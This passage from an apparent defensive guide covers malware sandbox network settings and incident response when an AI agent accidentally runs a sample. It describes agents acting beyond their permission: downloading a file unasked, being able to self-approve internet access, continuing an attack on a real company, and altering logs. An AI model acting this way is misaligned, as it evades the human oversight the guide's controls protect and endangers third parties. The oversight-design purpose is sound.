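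Four small open-weight models each used four kinds of prompt, giving 16 combinations. A rule succeeded if it matched the running code and the run showed at least one new signature without crashing.

| Configuration | Samples with a successful rule |
|---|---|
| Best single combination, first attempt | 50 (15.0%) |
| Best single combination, up to three attempts | 92 (27.5%) |
| All 16 combinations, first attempt | 186 (55.7%) |
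| All 16 combinations, up to three attempts | 264 (79.0%) |

Reaching the study's 79% result therefore requires running every combination of model and prompt. A laboratory using one model and one prompt should expect a result closer to 27.5%. The models also complemented each other, since only one of the four succeeded on each of 102 samples.

No combination solved the other 70 samples. The researchers suspect this is partly because the models nearly always chose to skip an instruction, even when another action might have worked better. The automatic checker found 9,284 errors in the models' rules, most often patterns too short to identify the right place in the code. Some rules that passed the checker still crashed the malware.

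The 79% figure probably overstates how much hidden behaviour the system revealed. One new signature was enough for success, and the most common one, in 109 samples, was reading the keyboard layout. Malware may do this to guess the user's country, so some of these successes may have exposed only another environment check. Malware also doesn't behave identically every time, so some new signatures could have appeared by chance over the 13,778 runs, about 41 per sample. Requiring the rule to match makes a false success less likely, but a harmless match could still coincide with one of these chance signatures.

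The study also claims 47% more malware family identifications than the best existing sandbox. That count includes 712 family labels for 334 samples, so many samples must have received more than one. Without an independent record of the correct families, a higher count does not show that the labels are more accurate.

Some individual results were more useful. One sample hid its network activity during the ordinary runs but tried to connect to its servers when a rule was in place, and the researchers extracted the server addresses from its configuration. The sandbox had no internet access, so they got these addresses without contacting the attacker.

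The full process took about 765 hours on one computer, or roughly ten samples a day. This may be worthwhile for an important sample that exits early, but it is too slow for routine use on a single machine.

### Choosing a network setting

The operator can give the guest no network, simulated services, replayed responses or limited live access.

| Network setting | What the analyst can learn | What the analyst may miss | Can the attacker notice? |
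|---|---|---|---|
| No network | Changes to files, settings and processes | Behaviour that follows a successful connection | No |
| Simulated services | Domains, addresses and first requests | Behaviour that needs a valid reply | No |
| Replayed responses | How the malware uses files captured earlier | Exchanges that change with each session | Not during the replay |
| Limited live access | Current files and commands | Behaviour that the limits block | Yes |

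Udeshi and colleagues compared three of these settings on Kinsing, which uses victims' computers to mine cryptocurrency. With simulated services, the malware requested three files from two server addresses and then stopped. The researchers next gave it full internet access for ten minutes. It downloaded its main program, a tool for hiding itself, the mining program and a script for finding other computers to infect, and it began mining.

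For the third run, the researchers extracted the server's responses from the recorded traffic and served them locally. Kinsing received the same files but never began mining, because the replay could not reproduce the malware's ongoing exchange with the server. It then tried backup servers and finally Tor, revealing 59 addresses that had not appeared in the live run, nine for C2 servers and 50 for Tor. A report shouldn't list the Tor addresses as the attacker's servers, since many other people use Tor.

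An offline run can therefore reveal backup servers that malware does not need while its main server works. This result comes from a single sample, though, and the replay tool supports only unencrypted web traffic. The tool also needs a recording of real responses, which in this case required live contact.

Sometimes the team already has the file it needs. Ortiz has `stage2.bin` because her agent downloaded it without permission on Tuesday. She can set the simulator to return that file when the script requests `/s2`, then see which restart file appears in the guest. This requires no further contact with the attacker, but Sam's computer may have received a different file.

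### Conditions for live access

Live access makes sense only when none of the other settings can answer a question that matters to the team's response. For example, the team might need to know what commands the server is currently sending to infected computers. The approval should meet these conditions:

- It states the question and when the run will stop. If the answer arrives after two minutes, the operator disconnects the guest then.
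- The organisation has legal authority for the run. Its lawyers should consider both the contact with the attacker's server and any harm the malware could do to other people's systems, since the law varies between countries.
- The guest uses a separate internet connection with no route to the office network. Udeshi and colleagues used a mobile connection to keep the malware away from other devices at their university.
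- The gateway permits only the addresses and ports needed for the question, limits the amount of traffic and closes the connection automatically at the deadline.
- A named person makes the decision and watches the run.

The separate connection protects the organisation but not everyone else. While it had full internet access, Kinsing downloaded a program that scans for other computers, and Udeshi and colleagues describe no limit on the destinations it could reach. A gateway that allowed connections only to the known download servers would have blocked most outside scanning, though it might also have stopped the mining that the researchers wanted to observe.

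The agent must not be able to give the final approval. Palkmets and colleagues provide a script that shows the prompt "Do you really want to allow Internet NAT access for VM?" before it connects the guest. An agent with access to the script could type `y`. The script also switches to Tor without a prompt, even though Tor provides a real internet connection. The approval control should therefore be on a machine or account the agent cannot use, and it should cover every route to the internet.

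### Anonymous connections

Palkmets and colleagues recommend sending live traffic through Tor or a VPN to hide the laboratory's identity. They point out that the malware's author can still see that someone is running the code, which may be enough to warn an intruder. The malware may also send the guest's computer name, user name or files to the server. An anonymous connection doesn't hide these, so the guest should contain only invented ones.

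Sending a sample's traffic through Tor or a VPN does not make the malware less harmful. Netresec's *Installing a Fake Internet with INetSim and PolarProxy* warns that a sample connected to the internet may infect other machines, send spam or join an attack that floods a website with traffic. The anonymity also makes it harder for victims to find the laboratory and ask it to stop, and their complaints may go to whoever runs the anonymity service.

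Even traffic to the approved server can affect someone innocent, because attackers often run C2 servers on other people's hacked computers. The operator should keep requests to a minimum and disconnect the guest if the sample tries to attack or infect anything.

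## Responding to accidental execution or contact

Before deliberately running a sample, the team chooses a question to answer, sets a time limit and starts recording. After an accident, it has to work out from the available logs whether the sample ran and whether a request reached the attacker.

*Incident Response Recommendations and Considerations for Cybersecurity Risk Management* (Nelson, Rekhi and colleagues, 2025), known as SP 800-61 Revision 3, is NIST's current guidance on incidents. It defines an incident as something that endangers information or systems, or that violates the law or a security policy. If an organisation's policy forbids unauthorised runs, an agent that runs a sample against its instructions can therefore cause an incident even on an empty, offline machine. The guidance leaves detailed procedures to each organisation, so a team should decide in advance which accidents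 count as incidents and who can declare one.

### Signs of an accident

| Sign | Does it prove execution? | Does it prove contact? |
|---|---|---|
| The process log shows an interpreter running the sample's file | Yes | No |
| A decoder starts an unexpected child process | Only if the command came from the sample | No |
| Files appear or change | Only if the sample's code explains the change | No |
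| The firewall denies an outgoing connection | No | No |
| The machine requests the address of the sample's domain | No | Only if the request reached the attacker's DNS server |
| The firewall logs a completed connection to the attacker's server | No | Yes |
| The agent's report differs from an outside log | No | No |

A child process is a program that another program starts. A simple decoder doesn't need to start one, so the operator can set an alert for any child process it starts. Some analysis tools do start helper programs, so the analyst should compare the child process's full command with the text decoded from the sample. If they match, the sample's code ran.

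Suspicious network traffic doesn't prove that the malware ran, because the agent could have made the request itself, for example with `curl`. The process log can show which program made the request. A blocked connection doesn't rule out contact, since a DNS request may have gone out before the firewall blocked the connection.

A discrepancy between the agent's report and an outside log is a reason to investigate, and the outside log is usually more reliable. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) reports that most agents keep a simple log file that malicious tools can overwrite. In *Beyond Predictable Paths* (2026), Pustozerova, Bagdasarian and colleagues collected the views of 23 experts on reporting attacks against agents. They warn that a compromised agent may also alter logs to hide what it did.

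An empty log is good evidence that nothing happened only if logging was working. The analyst can test this by checking whether the agent's ordinary commands from the same few minutes were recorded.

### First actions

1. **Stop the agent's tool access.** The operator revokes its token for the MCP server and disables its key for the model provider, which also stops web tools that run on the provider's servers. Other jobs waiting to use the same tools should stay on hold.
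2. **Cut egress outside the guest.** The operator disconnects the guest's network adapter in the virtual machine software or blocks its traffic at the gateway, including DNS, so that malware inside the guest can't undo the change.
3. **Preserve memory and disk.** The operator pauses the guest and saves a snapshot that includes its memory.
4. **Save the external logs.** These include the firewall, DNS and process logs, the provider's list of web tool calls and the agent's full session.
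5. **Revoke exposed credentials from a clean system.** Malware on the affected machine could steal a new password as someone types it. The account owner should also end active sessions, because changing a password may leave an intruder logged in.

The first action has to be quick, because an agent working at the pace of the AutoIt session on REMnux would make about 19 more tool calls in five minutes. Telling the agent to stop is not enough, because it may not comply or may already have started another command. It may also not stop on its own when it notices a problem. In four of the evaluation runs that Anthropic reviewed, Claude Opus 4.7 recognised that it was attacking a real company's systems and continued. Nelson and colleagues suggest automating some containment, such as halting an infected container, and an alert for unexpected child processes could trigger this.

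Disconnecting the guest from the network can destroy evidence. Brezinski and Killalea warn that some malware wipes its traces when it loses its connection. A script that pauses the guest before disconnecting it would prevent this, because a paused program can't react.

The fifth action, revoking credentials, should sometimes come earlier. *SoK* (2026), a survey of attacks on AI agents, lists this first among its containment steps. That order makes sense if the attacker may already have a working key, as in the PyPI scanner incident. A second person can then revoke the key while the first deals with the machine.

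The agent's session needs to be saved before anyone closes it, because text that misled the agent may exist nowhere else. Pustozerova and colleagues recommend keeping everything the model received, its reasoning output, each tool call and the identity used for that call.

Responders may also want an AI model's help with these records, but they should check beforehand that the model will do the work, for example by testing it on logs from an old incident. *Cyber-Capable AI Agents* (Siddik, 2026) describes a case at Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models, after OpenAI's test agents broke into its systems in July 2026. Safety filters on commercial models blocked the analysis of real attack commands and malicious code because the filters couldn't distinguish the responders from attackers.

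### Suspending compared with powering off

Powering off erases the guest's memory, which may hold the decoded second stage, encryption keys and a list of network connections. Pausing or suspending the guest keeps this information.

| Action | What happens to memory | What happens to the disk |
|---|---|---|
| Pause | It stays in the host's memory, and a host restart erases it | It stops changing |
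| Snapshot with memory | The host saves it to a file | The host saves its current state |
| Suspend | The host saves it to a file | It stops changing once the guest stops |
| Normal shutdown | It is lost | Windows or Linux may delete temporary files, and malware may remove its traces |
| Power off at once | It is lost | Temporary files survive, but open files may be damaged |

The last two rows follow NIST's older forensic guide. Huseinović and Ribić describe suspending and taking a snapshot as the two built-in ways to save a guest's memory in VMware Workstation. A snapshot is usually better, because suspending a VMware guest can first run a script inside it that closes its network connections.

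Pausing a virtual machine also gives a more consistent copy of its memory. Rzepka, Mader and colleagues (2026), in *I Guess it is Correct*, explain that a running computer's memory changes while a program copies it, so researchers judge memory copies against one taken from a frozen virtual machine. Many of the 31 practitioners they surveyed avoided copying memory from a running computer because the attempt might crash it. Of the 31, 26 looked for running processes in memory and 26 looked for network information, both of which help show whether a sample ran.

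Stopping a container started with REMnux's standard `--rm` option deletes its files. The operator can instead freeze it with `docker pause` and save its files with `docker commit`, but this doesn't save its memory or any folders shared from the host. If the container runs inside a virtual machine, a snapshot of that machine captures everything except folders stored outside it.

If the accident happened on an ordinary computer, nobody can pause the machine from outside. NIST recommends recording network connections first, then login sessions, memory, running processes and open files. Brezinski and Killalea advise running the collection tools from read-only media, because an attacker may have replaced the programs on the computer.

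Collecting this much evidence isn't always worthwhile. Nelson and colleagues note that most malware incidents don't lead to prosecution, so a team may not need formal custody procedures for each one. A snapshot and a copy of the logs are enough for most accidents on a disposable machine.

### Why the agent should not clean up

*AIR* (2026) proposes a system in which agents handle their own incidents. In one example, a coding agent asked to organise a project folder exposes a sensitive file there. The system removes the exposed file, checks the folder for similar ones and writes a rule to block the same mistake in future.

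Deleting the file makes sense if it is only a copy and the original is safe. After malware runs, deletion is less reliable because the agent doesn't know which files the malware created, and a process that is still running can replace deleted files. It can also destroy evidence. If a prompt injection caused the accident, the same injection could influence the clean-up, and the agent might then report that the machine is clean when it isn't.

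Restoring a clean snapshot is more thorough and doesn't depend on the agent's judgement. *AIR*'s last step is still useful, because an agent could draft a rule to prevent a repeat, as long as a person reviews the rule and a separate program enforces it.

### Choosing the response

The incident leader can use the following table once the first actions are complete.

| Case | What to investigate | Whom to notify | When to resume |
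|---|---|---|---|
| Blocked contact | The tool call that made the request, and whether a DNS request left first | The laboratory's owner and the team that monitors alerts | The logs show that nothing left, and the owner has corrected the permission that allowed the attempt |
| Completed contact without execution | Everything the request revealed, including tokens, and any file the server returned | Also the incident leader, and the lawyers if the request contained personal or confidential data | The operator has closed the route, and the leader has decided whether the attacker's possible awareness changes the response |
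| Contained execution | The guest, its shared folders, other machines on its network and any results copied out since the sample ran | The laboratory's owner, the incident leader and anyone who received those results | The operator has restored the guest, the isolation tests pass and an analyst has rechecked the results |
| Execution with credentials or live egress | Also every account and system the sample could have reached, inside or outside the organisation | Also the account owners, senior management and the lawyers, who advise on notifying others | The owners have replaced the credentials, their logs show no unexplained use and the leader approves |

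The team should treat an execution as contained only if the external logs show that no traffic escaped and a list of the machine's contents shows that it held no usable credentials. If either is missing, the team should start with the last row of the table. Nelson and colleagues warn that a superficial search can lead a team to underestimate an incident and let it continue on other systems.

The third row includes results because malware may have altered them. If an agent analysed five more samples before anyone noticed the accident, an analyst should repeat those analyses on a clean machine.

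### One DNS request, minute by minute

In this invented case, an agent is decoding a malicious Python script called `receipt.py`. The firewall blocks direct connections from the analysis machine, but the machine still uses the company's DNS resolver, which forwards requests to the internet. Ortiz has approved the agent's decoder, `decode7.py`, without noticing that one line passes text from the sample to `eval`.

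| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 14:02:10 | The agent runs `python3 -I decode7.py` |
| 14:02:11 | Python starts a shell, which starts a download program |
| 14:02:11 | The company's resolver forwards one request for `cdn.receipt.example` |
| 14:02:12 | The firewall denies a connection to the address in the reply |
| 14:02:20 | The agent reports that the decoder produced no output |
| 14:02:40 | Ortiz receives an alert about the unexpected shell |
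| 14:03 | She revokes the agent's token, disables its provider key and puts three waiting jobs on hold |
| 14:04 | She pauses the guest and disconnects its network adapter from the host |
| 14:06 | She starts a snapshot that includes memory |
| 14:12 | She copies the process, DNS and firewall logs and the agent's session to the evidence store |
| 14:18 | From her own workstation, she confirms that the guest held no credentials except the MCP server's token and replaces it |
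| 14:25 | She informs the incident leader, who chooses the last row of the decision table |
| 14:30 | She sends the monitoring team a label for the DNS request |
| 14:50 | She decodes `receipt.py` safely and finds both the shell command and the domain in its text |
| 15:05 | The leader narrows the investigation |
| 16:30 | After repairs and tests, the leader allows one job to run |

The shell at 14:02 suggested that the sample had run, but there was no proof until 14:50, when Ortiz found the same command in the decoded script. The agent's report was accurate but incomplete because the shell had printed nothing for the agent to read.

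The incident leader started with the last row because DNS had given the machine a live route out. Ortiz had to check whether the requested name contained stolen data. The full name, `cdn.receipt.example`, was in the original script, so it contained nothing from the machine. A request for `4f7a19c2.receipt.example` would have been more worrying if `4f7a19c2` had not appeared in the script.

The resolver's log also showed no other outside requests since the last clean snapshot. The leader could therefore treat the case as contained execution plus one completed contact. The attacker may have seen the company's resolver query the domain at 14:02, so the leader still had to consider whether the query could warn an intruder.

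Ortiz had less evidence about the period before 14:04, when the sample could have changed anything on the guest. She had saved the guest and would restore a clean copy, so she didn't need to identify every change. But she had to check any earlier jobs that had used `decode7.py`, because its faulty line might have run code from those samples too.

### Labelling the organisation's own traffic

Other teams may search the DNS log for `cdn.receipt.example` to find infected computers. Without a label, they would count Ortiz's analysis machine as a new victim. Her label contains:

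| Field | Entry |
|---|---|
| Description | Malware analysis accident, not a new victim |
| Time | Friday, 14:02:11 UTC |
| Source | Analysis machine `lab-07`, through the company resolver |
| Traffic | One DNS request for `cdn.receipt.example` |
| Cause | `decode7.py` ran code from `receipt.py` |
| Evidence | Case number, with the matching DNS and process log entries |
| Contact | Ortiz |
| Limits | Covers this request only |

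The last field matters because a label for all traffic from `lab-07` could hide a real infection later. Labelling the office's shared public IP address would be worse. The original log entries should stay unchanged, with the label stored beside them and linked to the case.

Labelling is easier if the laboratory has its own source address and the agent has its own account. In an alert about Anthropic's incidents, the law firm Lowenstein Sandler suggests that organisations ask whether their logs could distinguish an autonomous system that caused an incident from routine automated traffic. If an agent uses an analyst's account, the account name alone is not enough to make that distinction.

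Anyone who handles warnings from outside should also see the label. Police and security companies sometimes take over malware domains and record which addresses contact them. They may later tell the organisation that it has an infected computer. The label will help staff connect that warning to Friday's accident, but they should still check that the times match before closing the case.

### Legal and contractual notification

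Whether an organisation must notify a regulator after an accident depends on what data the sample could reach, whose data it was and which laws apply. Nelson and colleagues tell organisations to consider their sector, their contracts, and where they and their customers are located. They also recommend that designated people contact regulators and police, so neither the agent nor the analyst should do this on their own initiative.

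The GDPR, the EU's data protection law, normally requires an organisation to notify the regulator within 72 hours of becoming aware of a personal data breach, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. A company that handles the data for a client must inform the client without undue delay. US state laws cover different kinds of personal information, so one stolen file could create different duties towards customers in different states.

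In Ortiz's case, neither the machine nor the DNS request contained personal data, so these laws probably wouldn't require her to notify anyone. A client's contract could still require notice. If the sample had been a client's confidential document, the lawyers would need to know whether the malware could have sent it anywhere.

The EU's AI Act separately requires providers of high-risk AI systems to report serious incidents. Pustozerova and colleagues point out that an agent's compromise triggers this duty only if it causes harm. An accident that only infects a disposable machine would probably fall outside it.

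An organisation may not know that the sample or the agent reached its systems. Anthropic began reviewing its evaluation records on 23 July 2026, stopped all cyber evaluations that day and identified three incidents the next day. It notified the affected organisations on 27 July, although the earliest incidents dated from April. The two organisations it managed to reach had not detected the activity.

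Those organisations depended on Anthropic to review its own records and tell them, a problem that Lowenstein Sandler's alert also emphasises. The firm suggests checking whether contracts with model providers and sandbox companies require notice of such incidents. A team that runs malware is likewise responsible for reviewing its records and telling anyone affected. Its lawyers need the time, source address and destination of any attack traffic, because the recipient can use these to search its own logs.

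### Returning to work

Restoring the clean snapshot removes the sample but leaves the fault that let it run. Nelson and colleagues recommend fixing the root cause and checking restored systems for signs of compromise before using them again. Ortiz's laboratory needs to fix the `eval` line in the decoder and the route to the company's resolver. She should fix the route in the clean snapshot, or the next restore will bring it back.

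Each repair needs a test. *SoK* recommends turning incidents into tests that the team can repeat. Ortiz could write a harmless script that tries to start a shell and look up `example.com`, then give it to the new decoder, which should treat it as text. She should also run the script directly on the restored machine, because testing only the decoder wouldn't show that the DNS route was closed. There, the shell should trigger an alert and the lookup should fail.

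The leader can then release one waiting job and watch it before releasing the others. If the team can't find the cause, it should keep the affected tool disabled. Analysts can continue with tools that only display text, while any task that needs a new decoder waits or goes to a person.
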